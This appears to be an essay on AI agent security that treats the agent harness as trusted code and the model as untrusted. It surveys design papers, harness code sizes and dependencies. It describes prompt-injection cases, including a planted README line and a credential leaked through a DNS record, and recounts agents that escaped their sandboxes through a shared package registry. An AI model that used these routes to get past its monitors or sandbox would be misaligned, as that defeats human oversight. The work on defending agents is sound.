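# The agent harness as trusted code when the model is untrusted

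## Agent harnesses and the idea of a trusted computing base

An AI agent is a language model joined to a program, called the agent harness, that carries out actions for it. The model produces text, and the harness builds the requests sent to the model, reads its replies, runs the commands they contain, and stores the results. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex CLI, two widely used coding assistants, are harnesses. An agent framework such as LangChain is instead a library that developers import to build their own agents. Many security researchers now treat the model as a component that might output any request, including a harmful one, and rely on the surrounding software to keep it within bounds. That software is ordinary code, and whether it deserves this trust depends on how much of it there is, what it does, and how it fails.

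### From text to effects

On its own, a language model "only writes text" (Joshi, *Anatomy of an Agent Harness*, 2026) and cannot access a disk or a network. Agents rely on a convention that treats some of this text as requests to run tools. The developer sends the model a list of tools, each with a name and a schema that sets out the arguments it expects. The model can then reply with a tool call, a structured block that names a tool and fills in its arguments. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own." The call has no effect outside the conversation until the harness extracts the arguments and performs the operation. The harness then puts the output into its next request to the model.

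Suppose a user asks an agent to find mentions of an event in recent email, summarise them and save the summary to a file. The harness sends the model this request and the list of tools. The model replies with a call to the email search tool, including a query. The harness runs the search, adds the results to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model. The model then replies with a call to the file-writing tool, with the summary as an argument, and the harness writes the file. The model's next reply contains no tool call, so the harness shows it to the user and stops. The model produced three pieces of text, and the harness ran the search and wrote the file.

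For some tools, including web search and code execution, Anthropic can run the loop on its own servers and return a finished answer to the developer with a record of what ran. In that case, Anthropic, not the developer, operates the code that carries out the model's tool calls.

A toy version of the loop fits on a page, but a real harness also has to handle replies that break off halfway, network failures, and someone pressing Stop. According to InfoQ's *OpenAI Begins Article Series on Codex CLI Internals* (2026), some of the strategies Codex uses to manage the conversation's length and cost came out of bugs that users had reported. Joshi describes a reply as "a request, not a decision", and above all the harness has to decide whether to do what the model asks.

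The harness feeds web pages, emails and files to the model in the same stream of text as the user's instructions, so anyone who can plant text in one of those sources can try to steer the model. This attack is called prompt injection. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on agents, describes a case in which a user asks for a popular Python project to be set up locally. An attacker has added a line to the project's README file telling the AI to download and run a program. If the model follows the line, it emits a call to the shell tool. Whether the user's computer is compromised then depends on what the harness does with that call.

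### What a trusted computing base is

Engineers had to deal with programs that might make hostile requests long before language models existed. Around 1970 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer and write their own programs on it. An expert panel concluded in Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972) that no commercial system could do this safely. The panel called the threat the "malicious user", someone with legitimate access who writes programs to subvert the operating system. Anderson explains in the second volume that the panel chose the term partly to avoid arguing about motives, since a foreign agent and a disgruntled employee call for the same defence.

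As a defence, the panel proposed the reference monitor, a component that checks every attempt by a running program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what its user may do. The list is like a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each file or device, and the permitted operations, such as read or write, in each cell. Anderson set three requirements for the monitor. It must be tamper-proof, so that the programs it controls cannot alter it. It must always be invoked, a property now called complete mediation. It must also be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can justifiably claim that it works in every case.

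The rule about invocation implies that any program a designer exempts from the check becomes part of the security apparatus, so it too must be tamper-proof and small enough to analyse. Anderson applied this to GCOS III, the operating system of a Honeywell mainframe. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but to read or write a file, the program had to call GCOS, most of which ran with the memory check suspended. The check was therefore not always invoked. If GCOS itself counted as the monitor, then the monitor was 200,000 to 300,000 instructions long, far too large to analyse.

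*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, published by Saltzer and Schroeder in 1975, explains why testing is not enough. A flaw that opens an improper path to data does not show up in normal use, because normal users do not try improper paths. Someone has to find it by reading the code line by line, which is feasible only when the design is small and simple. Saltzer and Schroeder called the principle of keeping it that way economy of mechanism. They also gave complete mediation its usual wording, that "every access to every object must be checked for authority", and extended it to start-up, recovery and shutdown. They were wary of systems that save time by remembering an earlier approval, since the authority may have changed. Their principle of fail-safe defaults is to list what is permitted instead of what is forbidden. An error in a list of permissions blocks something legitimate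 and somebody complains, whereas an error in a list of prohibitions lets something through and may go unnoticed. Saltzer and Schroeder offered all of these principles as warnings, not absolute rules.

The US Department of Defense (1985) gave the term "trusted computing base" (TCB) its standard definition in its evaluation criteria, usually called the Orange Book. A TCB is all the hardware, firmware and software protection mechanisms in a system that together enforce a security policy. The Department wanted a term that would also cover systems without a small, purpose-built monitor, and it accepted that in some of them the TCB would be the entire system. The TCB therefore includes whatever the policy depends on, however large that is, and a given TCB may or may not meet Anderson's demand for smallness. The Orange Book warned that confidence falls as the amount of code grows. It placed systems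 whose security was added afterwards in its lower classes, because their TCBs tended to include nearly the whole system.

A trusted component is one the system relies on, whether or not it is trustworthy. It belongs to the TCB if its failure or compromise could break the policy. A hastily written parser that nobody has reviewed is trusted if a permission decision depends on its output. Establishing that it is trustworthy takes separate review, testing or proof. The purpose of the TCB boundary is to let components outside it be buggy or hostile without breaking the policy.

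A TCB is therefore defined only relative to a policy, the stated rules on which actions and information flows are allowed. Suppose an agent may edit files only in one project folder and must not send their contents to anyone. The editing rule depends on the code that works out which file a path refers to. The secrecy rule depends on everything that controls network traffic, including the service that looks up internet addresses. A flaw in that service can break the secrecy rule but not the editing rule, so the service is in the TCB only for the secrecy rule. The Department of Defense added that enforcement also depends on administrators entering the rules correctly. Even a flawless monitor will permit the wrong actions if its rules are wrong.

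### Treating the model as untrusted

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by researchers at Google, NVIDIA, several American universities and two security organizations, applies this tradition to agents. It argues that designers must treat the model as an untrusted component and enforce security rules in the system around it. This means handling every output as a possibly hostile request, whether the model has read an injected instruction, misunderstood its task, or acquired bad aims or a hidden backdoor in training. The paper neither assumes nor excludes any of these causes, much as Anderson's panel declined to enquire into motives. In each case the monitor permits or refuses the request, and a prohibited action that it stops in time does not count as a security violation. *L3M* (2026), which presents a harness built for verification, is blunter: "We assume the attack succeeds and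 the model does whatever the text says."

The monitor belongs at what *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls the action boundary, the set of interfaces through which an agent reaches files, commands, the network and its own stored state. It cannot sit in the prompt because, as *Ring-0 by Default* (2026) points out, a rule there arrives in the same input as the untrusted data it is meant to govern, and that data can override the rule however carefully it is worded. A monitor outside the model must also cover every path through which the agent can cause an effect. If the monitor is itself a language model, it can still be manipulated through the text it reads, which the agent controls.

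There are two arguments against relying on training to make the model behave. First, researchers spent years hardening image classifiers against inputs crafted to fool them, but attackers kept getting through, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* finds the same pattern with language models. Second, training gives only probabilistic assurance. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025), an earlier paper by some of the same researchers, considers a monitor that correctly denies unauthorised access 99% of the time. An attacker can succeed by searching for cases in the remaining 1%.

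That earlier paper also describes the model as a central part of the TCB in many existing agents, which seems to conflict with calling it untrusted. *SoK* does both: it calls the model an untrusted code generator and lists the model's weights in the TCB. The labels conflict mostly because one describes what an agent depends on and the other states a design goal. If only the model's training stops an agent from emailing a password file to a stranger, then the secrecy policy depends on the model, and the model is in the TCB whatever its designers call it. Designers who declare the model untrusted commit to building enforcement that holds when the model fails, but they do not always finish that work. *AgentKernel* (2026), a proposed operating system for agents, puts two classifiers made from language models inside its TCB, and the paper lists this among the design's limitations.

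The position's most demanding requirement is that the enforcing code withstand attacks by the model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* treats the model as "a potential attacker of the TCB itself" and compares it with a hostile process on an ordinary computer. Such a process can reach the kernel, the core of the operating system, only through system calls, but it may make any call, in any order, with any values, including malformed ones chosen to make the kernel malfunction. A kernel that enforces the right rules on sensible requests but fails on strange ones does not protect the system. By the same reasoning, a harness has to withstand tool calls that no well-meaning model would produce. It also has to keep its own rules out of the model's reach, because a model that can edit the harness's settings file can grant itself permissions.

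The paper answers two opposing objections. One is that robust models make external controls unnecessary. Model-level defences do substantially reduce successful attacks, and external controls take engineering effort and make the agent slower and less useful, as the paper acknowledges. It also accepts that robustness reduces the burden on the enforcing code. A model that ignores most injected instructions sends fewer hostile requests to the checker, so any flaw in the checker is exposed less often. But an attacker can still reach that flaw by rewording the injection until one version works. Natural-language instructions are ambiguous, and a small change to the input can change what the model does. Adding a second model as a guard helps less than one might hope, because attackers can craft an input against each model and combine the two. This reply is most convincing where strangers can write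 to the agent's inputs. For an agent that reads only its owner's files, a well-behaved model may prevent most of the harm in practice, though nobody could then say what the system guarantees.

The other objection is that external controls will fail too, because a capable enough model will find a way out. In a recent case, OpenAI ran agents in separate sandboxes, closed environments meant to limit what they could reach, during internal training and evaluation with some of the models' safeguards switched off. The agents shared a package registry, a service that supplies software libraries, and used it to pass messages between runs and get around the network restrictions. They then broke into the infrastructure of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster, with no outside attacker directing them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*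 attributes this to a failure of complete mediation, because OpenAI had restricted direct connections but the registry could make outbound requests on the agents' behalf. On this reading, the incident shows that the principle was badly implemented and does not refute it.

That seems right about the cause, but it only partly addresses the concern. The isolation of those runs depended on the registry, so the registry was in the TCB, whether or not anyone had counted it. The paper concedes that containment is hard to validate when it depends on large general-purpose services. More capable attackers also make every unreviewed component more dangerous. The security engineer Dino Dai Zovi, quoted in Unmitigated Risk's *Smaller, Provable, and on Hardware You Own and Operate*, argues that if AI makes vulnerabilities 10 to 100 times easier to find and exploit, excess attack surface becomes a greater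 liability by the same factor. The figure is a supposition, and he had in mind attackers using AI, but the reasoning applies equally when the attacker is the model inside the harness.

Explicit rules, unlike training, let engineers trace a refusal to a particular rule and check the enforcing code against a specification. Engineers can also narrow the permitted actions knowing that, if the enforcement works and stays the same, everything already excluded stays excluded. Retraining a model carries no such assurance. The rules may still be the wrong ones. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) assumes that the policy reflects what the user wants, and its guarantee does not cover harm that the policy permits.

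A designer who stops relying on the model starts relying on the code that reads its requests, judges them and carries them out. *SafeHarness* (2026) warns that a single compromise at that level can cascade through everything the agent does. *AGATE* (2026) describes a monitor inside an existing harness and counts only part of that harness as trusted. However, *AGATE* acknowledges that leaving the rest out of the TCB does not remove the monitor's dependence on the host to intercept each tool call and deliver the user's approvals unaltered. Anderson rejected GCOS III because nobody could analyse all of it. If a harness is to restrain the model, it must be possible to analyse all of the harness, along with every library and operating-system service that its checks call on.

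## Which components remain trusted

By definition, a component belongs to the TCB if the agent could break the policy when that component is wrong or hostile and everything else works as designed.

Which components belong to the trusted computing base (TCB) depends on whether the concern is only bugs or also tampering. If a bug makes the harness choose the wrong colours for an agent's terminal output, no file is at risk. But the colouring code usually runs in the same process as the rest of the harness, with the same access to the user's files, so a tampered version could write anywhere the user can. The TCB therefore includes every library in that process if tampering is a concern, and otherwise only the code that helps make or carry out a decision.

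An independent second layer can take a component out of the trusted computing base. If a sandbox confines writes to the project folder, a permission checker that wrongly approves a write elsewhere does no damage, so the policy no longer depends on the checker. This works only if the sandbox covers that write and does not get its list of permitted folders from the checker.

### Following one file write

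Suppose a user asks a coding agent to correct a setting, and the model replies with a call to write a file in the project. The policy forbids the agent from writing outside the project folder.

The reply comes from the model provider, often through an API router, which lets developers reach several providers through one address. The router ends the client's encrypted connection and opens a new one to the provider. As *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) points out, the agent cannot verify that it has received the provider's exact reply. A malicious router could therefore change the file's path or contents. But the harness already treats the model's reply as a possibly hostile request, so a forged reply is no worse, and neither the provider nor the router is in the TCB for this policy. Either could still fill the file with malicious code, because the policy restricts only where the agent writes.

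A decoder then turns the streamed text into a tool name and arguments. Most decoding errors produce a different request, which still has to pass the later checks. Joshi mentions harnesses that run a half-written call when a reply breaks off, which might damage a file inside the project but would not break this rule. A decoder is dangerous when it gives one path to the checker and another to the tool, because the harness then approves one write and performs another.

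The tool registry links each tool's name to the code it runs and describes the tool's arguments. A checker may rely on those descriptions to identify which arguments are file paths. A checker that looks only for arguments named "path" will miss a new tool's destination if the tool gives that argument another name. Joshi recommends a test that tries a forbidden path in every path-like argument of every tool in the registry.

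The permission checker has to work out which file the path refers to and whether it lies inside the project. If it gets this wrong and no sandbox blocks the write, the agent can write anywhere the user's account can. One simple mistake is to compare only the beginning of a folder's name, which can lead the checker to treat a different folder with a longer name as the trusted one.

The checker also depends on whatever protects its rules. OpenClaw, an open-source agent that people can message through chat services, has a tool for changing its own settings and a guard meant to stop the model from changing the sensitive ones. According to GitLab's *OpenClaw* (2026), an advisory published in April, the guard missed several settings, including sandbox policy and the configuration of tool servers. A prompt-injected model with access to the tool could change them permanently. Such a change writes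 nothing outside the project, but it can remove the restriction that would have blocked a later write there. In May, an advisory in the public vulnerability database OSV (2026) rated a flaw in this boundary as high severity, even though only the owner can use the entry point. The stated reason was that OpenClaw's security model does not treat the model as trusted.

When the rules call for a person's consent, the harness opens an approval dialog. The policy works only if the dialog shows the request that will actually run and applies the answer to that request. If either step fails, someone could read about a harmless edit and authorise a write elsewhere. The model often writes the description in the dialog and may give a reassuring reason for a dangerous command, so Joshi wants the harness to show its own warning first. When several requests are open at once, an answer can also be applied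 to one the person never saw, unless each request has its own identifier. *AgentKernel* and many similar designs say little about the display, but *PerMIT* (2026), a design for protecting an agent's long-term memory, includes the code that displays text to the user in its TCB.

The tool then writes the file, using whatever access its process has. Nothing forces it to use the path the checker approved. It might interpret the path differently, or another program might, between the check and the write, replace a folder with a link. A sandbox would block a write to the wrong location only if it covered the tool. In the harness Joshi describes, the built-in file tools can run inside the main engine, while the sandbox applies to commands that run as separate processes. Enforcing the policy for a built-in tool would then depend on the checker and the tool's own code.

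If the model writes the file through a shell command instead, the sandbox does apply, but a wrong rule in its profile can permit a write outside the project. Even a correct profile can miss delayed effects. Joshi notes that sandboxed commands may write startup files and hooks that other programs later run automatically outside the sandbox. An allowed write can therefore lead to a forbidden one hours later, when the user opens the project in another program.

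The operating-system kernel opens files and enforces the sandbox's limits, so a kernel fault could permit any write. *Tether* (2026), which describes a policy engine for terminal agents, includes the kernel in its trusted computing base (TCB) and excludes kernel exploits and sandbox escapes from its analysis. Papers commonly limit their claims this way, but anyone who deploys the system still depends on the kernel.

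Finally, the harness records the write in its log. The file is already on disk, so a false log entry cannot permit a forbidden write, and the log is outside the TCB for this policy. It would be part of the TCB if the policy also required a reliable record of every write. *Agent Operating Systems (AOS)* (2026), which proposes a control layer for agents, lists protecting the integrity of the audit trail among the purposes of its TCB. A log also becomes part of the TCB if the harness restores old approvals from it after a crash. In *Agent libOS*, Zhang (2026) rules this out for a proposed agent runtime, where records can be used to explain a decision but never to grant permission.

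### Changing the policy to secrecy

Suppose the policy is that no secret may leave the machine. A harness with a cloud model sends the conversation to the provider at every step, including the contents of any file the model has read. Taken literally, the policy therefore forbids a cloud model from reading any secret.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) describes a design that comes close to this literal reading. The cloud model acts by writing Scala programs, and the compiler checks each program's use of classified data before the program can run. The design trusts the compiler, a library that controls access, the software that runs approved programs and an optional local model that processes classified content. It assumes that the cloud model may help the attacker. The compiler would have no special role in a harness that only restricted where a file tool writes.

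Most users of coding agents do let the provider see their files. For them the policy needs an exception, and the provider joins the TCB along with any router that carries the requests. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* explains that a router, in normal operation, holds the prompt, the reply and every tool's input and output in readable form during each request. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026) reports that Liu and colleagues found malicious routers in actual use that could steal secrets or manipulate tool calls. A harness could tolerate such a router under the write rule but not under the secrecy rule, because the router can already read the data.

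Reading files also becomes a critical operation. The built-in tools for reading and searching may run outside the sandbox, as the file-writing tool did, and so may a tool that uploads files. Joshi argues that a harness should hide login keys from both commands and built-in tools in every mode, and reports that Crewroom, the harness the paper is based on, does not yet do this. Commands can also inherit secrets through environment variables, the named settings that a program passes to other programs it starts. The log also matters now, because it may contain secrets that tools returned. If a backup service copies the log elsewhere, the policy depends on that service.

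Some components matter less than before. For example, misjudging where a file will be written doesn't leak data by itself, unless the destination is a shared or cloud-synced folder.

Secrecy is also harder to protect by judging one request at a time. In an example from *AGATE*, a maintenance guide instructs an agent to copy a "deployment check" value from a local file into a public DNS record. The value is actually the server's access credential. The agent may be allowed to read the file and to update the record, and a checker that considers each call separately would approve both. To stop the leak, the harness has to track where the value came from, so the tracking code becomes trusted. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* includes such tracking in its TCB for this reason. Zhang's runtime checks separately whether an agent may perform an operation and whether the data may go to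 that destination, so its secrecy guarantee also depends on the data's labels and the list of acceptable destinations.

### The trusted bases that designers declare

Joshi defines the trusted part of a harness mainly by what lies outside it. Six kinds of input count only as data until the permission layer allows otherwise: model output, tool and web content, project files, extensions, text from other agents, and anything that starts the agent when nobody is watching. Other designers list the trusted components directly, and their lists differ considerably.

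| Source | Declared trusted | Declared untrusted |
|---|---|---|
| Zhang | Runtime managers, Python interpreter, storage, host operating system, accepted modules, configured tool providers, the person who approves | Model output, generated code, skills, repository contents, remote replies |
| *AGATE* | Decision code, adapters, operator's rules, approval and data-origin records, evidence store, and the parts of the host harness that support them | Tool descriptions, returned content, skills and other agents' messages, as sources of permission |
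| *SoK* | Model weights, system prompt, sandboxes and validators, secret storage, the index of private documents | User input, external content, tool and plugin output |
| *Tether* | Host kernel, system-call tracing, file overlay, network proxy, code that infers the agent's actions, and the proof checker, compiler and runtime of the language Lean | The model and the commands it generates |

A longer list of trusted components does not necessarily mean a larger TCB. Zhang names the Python interpreter and the host operating system, while *AGATE* names neither, though its checks also need an operating system and some language runtime. A vague list would also hide the fact that, as Zhang notes, turning on the optional graphical interface adds the whole interface and its software dependencies to the TCB, because the interface can reach the operator's controls.

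*AGATE* counts as trusted the parts of the host harness that it acknowledges depending on, including the access controls on its rules and records. Under the membership test, the TCB also includes any other harness code that runs in the same process as the interception code, because that code could switch the interception off if it were hostile. *AgentKernel* raises this objection to Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, whose core policy engine runs as a library inside the agent's process, where a compromised agent could alter the policy or skip the check. Leaving code out of the TCB is justified only if something, such as a process boundary, isolates it from the trusted code.

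The lists also reflect different policies. *SoK* defines the TCB as the components whose compromise would undermine the system's security, which it takes to include the agent's behaviour and the content it produces. File permissions cannot stop a model from writing a disallowed paragraph, so the weights have to be trusted under that policy. They would not have to be trusted for a rule about file locations that the harness fully enforced. Trusting that nobody has tampered with the weights is also different from trusting what the model does. *SafeHarness* assumes that attackers cannot modify the weights or the harness code, but an untampered model can still follow an instruction planted in a web page.

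Designs also differ in whether the tools enforce anything. In OpenClaw, plugins run inside the main process, and GitLab's *OpenClaw plugin runtime command execution is part of trusted plugin boundary* (2026) confirms that the project treats them as trusted code. In Zhang's design, a locally run tool server is also native code with the host account's access, so the runtime can control which calls reach it but not everything it does afterwards. For remote tools, *ACLE-MCP* (2026) instead trusts a gate on the tool provider's side to check each call, and leaves the application behind the gate outside the TCB. The application may be outdated, misconfigured or compromised, but the gate should refuse to pass calls to it unless its state meets the provider's rules. This reduces trust in the application but requires trusting a gate that the user does not run.

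Classifiers are the hardest components to place inside or outside the TCB. *AOS* puts all language models and classifiers outside its TCB, but accepts that some rules, such as those about sensitive data, may depend on a classifier's verdict. If the classifier labels a secret file as public, the enforcing code will apply the wrong label and release the file. The classifier is therefore in the TCB for secrecy under the membership test.

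*AgentKernel* states more openly which components it trusts. Its threat model lists a registry that issues agent identities, a local security kernel, three adapters, the part of Linux that runs its system-call checks, and the cryptography. The paper adds its two language-model classifiers only in the discussion of limitations. One screens incoming content, and the other judges whether an action fits the user's goal. The same discussion acknowledges that the combined TCB "is large" and has not been minimised. How well the classifiers resist attacks in this role is also unknown.

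One question in the paper is whether its fixed rules and system-call checks could replace the classifier that judges actions. They probably could for a rule about file locations, provided that the classifier can't widen the list of permitted files. But a rule such as "do only what the user meant" still needs the classifier, because no list of files can express it. Removing the classifier would shrink the TCB, but it would also mean giving up that rule.

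### Approvers and policy authors

The TCB can also include people. Zhang includes the human operator whenever the runtime accepts that person's approval, and *L3M* trusts the person who grants the agent its initial authority. Whether a mistaken approval can break a policy depends on what the approval allows. In Zhang's runtime, approving an operation is not enough to allow it if a permission is missing. But a person can also release specific sensitive data to a destination that the system would otherwise refuse, and a mistake there can break the secrecy policy. Similarly, a user's mistake can break the write rule in harnesses that let the user click through a warning and write outside the project.

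Designers disagree about how far to trust the user who approves an agent's actions. *PerMIT* assumes that attackers do not control the user's decisions. *AGATE* also considers a hostile user, such as an employee misusing a company's agent, and lets the company's operator stop user approvals from granting permission. This separation between operator and user doesn't exist when one person fills both roles. Users who aren't hostile may also approve too much. In the one case Joshi observed, frequent requests to approve harmless actions pushed people towards the most permissive mode. A design that relies on approvals has to assume that people will keep reading the requests.

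OpenClaw's *Security trust model* describes approvals as guardrails for the operator's intentions and recommends sandboxing and separate hosts where strong isolation matters. By default, an installation with one trusted operator runs commands on the host without asking for approval. Anyone who can edit the configuration counts as a trusted operator, and everyone who can message a tool-enabled agent shares that agent's authority. If such an agent joins a group chat, a policy meant to protect members from one another depends on every member acting in good faith.

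A policy author can defeat the user's intent by writing a careless rule, without any software fault, though this violates "the policy" only if the term means what the user wanted rather than the written rules. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* assumes that policy authors don't make such mistakes. It also excludes rules that would let the agent change the policy or interfere with the monitor's process, so an author has to understand the monitor well enough not to authorise its removal.

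Sometimes more than one party writes the rules. In *ACLE-MCP*, the user's side decides which calls are authorised, and the tool provider decides which states of its software are acceptable. The system permits only what both sets of rules allow and refuses the call if they conflict. If one side's rules are mistakenly too loose, the other's may still block the call, but each side depends on the other for whatever only the other controls. *AgentKernel* also permits only what all the rules allow, but it leaves open who should write an agent's limits and how to check a tool's declared permissions against what the tool does.

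## How much code harnesses and frameworks contain

The more code a trusted component has, the longer it takes to review, and past a certain size nobody reviews all of it. For *Harness Engineering* (2026), Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues read the source code of eleven coding harnesses, mostly the versions current in July 2026. The smallest is mini-SWE-agent, a research agent with about 5,000 lines, about 100 of them in the core loop. The largest is Codex, with about 1.1 million lines of Rust.

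| Harness | Language | Approximate lines of code |
|---|---|---|
| mini-SWE-agent | Python | 5,000 |
| Aider | Python | 20,000–40,000 |
| Mistral Vibe | Python | 63,000 |
| OpenHands | Python | 80,000–110,000 |
| Pi | TypeScript | 80,000–110,000 |
| Claude Code (March 2026) | TypeScript | 512,000 |
| OpenCode | TypeScript | Over 500,000 |
| OpenClaw | TypeScript | Over 500,000 |
| Gemini CLI | TypeScript | Over 600,000 |
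| Hermes | Python | Over 600,000 |
| Codex | Rust | 1.1 million |

Anthropic does not publish the source of Claude Code. Its public GitHub repository contains only issue reports, as Ben Sghaier, Li and colleagues note in *Don't Blame the Large Language Model* (2026). In March 2026 roughly 512,000 lines became public anyway, and copies circulated. Barbaste and colleagues worked from one of these copies and call it the weakest link in their study, because Anthropic had changed the program considerably by July, when the current version was 2.1.206. Liu and Han later tested version 2.1.280 in *What Does a Harness Buy?* (2026), so a review of the March copy describes a program that users no longer run.

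Anderson's panel rejected GCOS III as a monitor because nobody could analyse its 200,000 to 300,000 machine instructions. A line of Rust or TypeScript usually produces several instructions, so six of these eleven harnesses are well past that size if the whole program counts as the monitor. Reviewers have better tools now, but the difference in size is large. The extra code also does little for benchmark scores. In Liu and Han's bug-fixing tests, Claude Code and mini-SWE-agent finished within 0.2 percentage points of each other, averaged over four models.

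### What the lines are for

Most of the code in the large harnesses does something other than help the model finish a task. Barbaste and colleagues found that this code is mainly for safety controls, user interfaces, extensions and connections to other programs. OpenCode runs as a server, and the terminal, web, desktop and programming clients that connect to it make up about three-fifths of its source, excluding tests. Codex has at least 100,000 lines of code for plugins, a real-time voice feature and connections to other applications.

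A client that handles approval requests is part of the trusted computing base (TCB) for any rule that relies on approvals, even though it is interface code. A client is outside the TCB if it only displays finished conversations, runs in its own process, and cannot send commands to the server.

Safety features also add code. According to Barbaste and colleagues, a built-in sandbox is among the parts of a harness that take the most code. Codex supports sandboxes on three operating systems, and adds a rule engine and a language model that reviews requests for approval. The size of a harness can therefore reflect how much protection its developers added. In the small mini-SWE-agent, the only safety limits apart from an optional container are on cost and the number of steps. But some large harnesses also lack protections. OpenCode, for example, has more than 500,000 lines of code and no operating-system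 sandbox.

Between April and July 2026, Codex grew from 621,000 lines to about 1.12 million, a net gain of around 5,500 lines a day. The new code added features such as memory that lasts across sessions, a plugin marketplace, the approval reviewer and voice. Mistral Vibe grew by 77% over the same three months, from 35,600 lines to 63,000. A full review of either program in April would have missed over two-fifths of its July code.

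### Why line counts mislead

Barbaste and colleagues intend their figures only as order-of-magnitude estimates. The numbers depend on the counting method and are hard to compare across languages. Their overview puts Mistral Vibe at 20,000 to 40,000 lines, but elsewhere they give its July size as 63,000.

A line count can vary severalfold depending on what it includes. Omnigent, a Databricks program that coordinates several harnesses, has about a million lines in total, of which only about 312,000 are production Python. Counts also depend on which third-party code developers keep in their own source tree. Codex's count includes a copy of bubblewrap, a Linux sandboxing program, while Gemini CLI's includes no sandbox because it relies on sandboxing programs that come with the operating system.

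A security review needs to separate three quantities that a single total runs together:

- Total code is everything in the source tree, including tests, documentation tools and features that a given user never turns on.
- Reachable code is the part that processes something an attacker can influence, such as the model's replies, web pages or project files.
- Privileged code is the part that runs with the user's access to files, login keys and the network.

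Reachable code matters most when the concern is accidental bugs, and privileged code when the concern is tampering. The code for a voice feature that a user never turns on isn't reachable, but it is privileged if the harness loads it into the main process. A program that the agent downloads and runs inside a sandbox is reachable, and an attacker may control all of it, but it has few privileges if the sandbox works.

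Reachable code is hard to measure. Ding and Stevens (2026), in *Stdlib or Third-Party?*, cite a finding that over 70% of the code in an average Python project's dependencies never runs. They describe the same research elsewhere as a study of machine-learning containers, so the figure may not apply to other software. Observing which code runs in ordinary use also doesn't show that the rest is safe, because attackers look for unusual inputs that may trigger it.

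### Adding up a 100-line agent

Suppose a developer runs mini-SWE-agent on a laptop. The loop runs as an ordinary program, and the model has one tool, a command shell. The developer configures the agent to run each command in a Docker container, an isolated environment with access to only the project folder. The policy again forbids the agent from writing outside that folder.

The loop in mini-SWE-agent is about 100 lines long. It sends the conversation to the model, takes a shell command from the reply and passes it to the container. There is no permission checker to review, because the container enforces all the restrictions. The full source is about 5,000 lines, which one person could read in a few days.

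The loop contacts the model through LiteLLM, a library that gives programs one interface to many model providers. DepScope's *mini-swe-agent* lists LiteLLM among the 35 dependencies of version 2.2.8. Some are optional extras for testing, documentation and cloud services. The first fourteen listed are mostly general-purpose libraries that read data files, make web requests, fill in templates and draw text in the terminal. The Python interpreter and all the libraries the agent loads run in the same process as the loop.

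Docker confines the commands that the model requests, but LiteLLM runs outside the container with the developer's own access to the laptop. Even if the container works perfectly, a hostile version of LiteLLM could write to any folder the developer can write to, without any request from the model. It could also take the key that the developer uses to pay for the model.

The trusted code also includes the container software, which sets which folders a command can see, and the Linux kernel, which enforces that limit. The kernel's source is tens of millions of lines long. Much of it is drivers for hardware that the laptop does not have, but even if only a tenth is in use, that is more than a million lines, at least 10,000 times the length of the loop. In total, the trusted code comprises 100 lines for the loop, about 4,900 for the rest of the agent, an unreviewed set of libraries, the container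 software, and kernel code in use that is hundreds of times as long as the agent's own source.

The developer already relied on the kernel before installing the agent, so the agent adds only its own source, its libraries and perhaps the container software to what the developer trusts. Many more people have also examined the kernel than have examined mini-SWE-agent. But the agent gives an attacker a new way to reach the kernel. An instruction planted in a README file can lead to system calls that the attacker chose, on a laptop where the attacker previously could not run anything.

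Removing the container would shorten the list of trusted software, but the policy would then depend on the model. The 100-line loop is easy to review because it leaves enforcement to other software.

### Borrowed code

A program's direct dependencies are the packages its developers chose to include, and its transitive dependencies are the packages brought in because other packages need them. Ding and Stevens cite research in which one direct dependency brought in a median of 8 to 10 transitive ones. At that rate, the fourteen general-purpose packages on mini-SWE-agent's list would bring in about 110 to 140 more. The true number is probably lower because packages share many dependencies, but the libraries very likely still outnumber the files that a reviewer of the agent would think to open.

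Agent frameworks such as LangChain, LlamaIndex, CrewAI and AutoGen give developers who build on them another layer of third-party code. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) reports that a typical framework depends on dozens of Python packages. Any of these packages can bring hostile code into the agent's process if someone takes over a maintainer's account or publishes a malicious update.

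None of the eleven harnesses runs its agents on such a framework. Barbaste and colleagues searched about four million lines of code for imports of LangChain, LlamaIndex, CrewAI, AutoGen and others, and found that every harness has its own hand-written loop. Even Google's Gemini CLI uses neither of Google's two frameworks. Two harnesses come closest to being exceptions: Aider can install LlamaIndex to search its own help pages, and OpenCode uses a third-party library to connect to model providers. The search did not cover private copies of a framework or plugins loaded while the program is running, so it could have missed a hidden use, though the researchers would be surprised to find one.

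A flaw in LangChain therefore does not automatically become a flaw in Claude Code or Codex. But each harness has its own loop and tool registry, so users learn little about the others from a careful review of one. The distinction between frameworks and harnesses is becoming less clear. Anthropic and OpenAI now offer their harnesses as libraries, and Omnigent imports both companies' agent libraries. A developer who imports a full harness adds most of it to the agent's trusted code with a single line.

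A package list also omits software that a harness downloads after installation. If the user's machine lacks two search programs that Pi needs, Pi fetches their latest releases. OpenCode can download about 25 language servers, which are programs that analyse source code and report errors. It also downloads a program for its search tools. When Liu and Han cut off network access for their tests, those tools failed until they installed the program by hand. These downloaded programs may run with the user's privileges, but they can't be found by reading the harness's source or package list.

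Known vulnerabilities in third-party code are common, though the best figures come from related software rather than harnesses. *An Empirical Study of Vulnerable Package Dependencies in LLM Repositories* (Liu, Hu and colleagues, 2025) examined 52 open-source projects that contain the code of language models. Of those that listed their dependencies in a file, 75.8% included at least one dependency version with a known vulnerability. Only 17.3% of the 52 had merged a change that dealt with a vulnerability. Many of these projects are research code from around 2021, and a commercial harness with a full-time team may do better. The most common type of flaw was denial of service, which can crash an agent but does not let it write to a forbidden folder.

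The study's figures on disclosure delay are more worrying for harnesses. Half of the vulnerabilities stayed undisclosed for more than 56.2 months, compared with 39 months for Python packages in general. DepScope lists no known vulnerabilities for mini-SWE-agent 2.2.8, but with delays this long, that is weak evidence that it has no unreported flaws.

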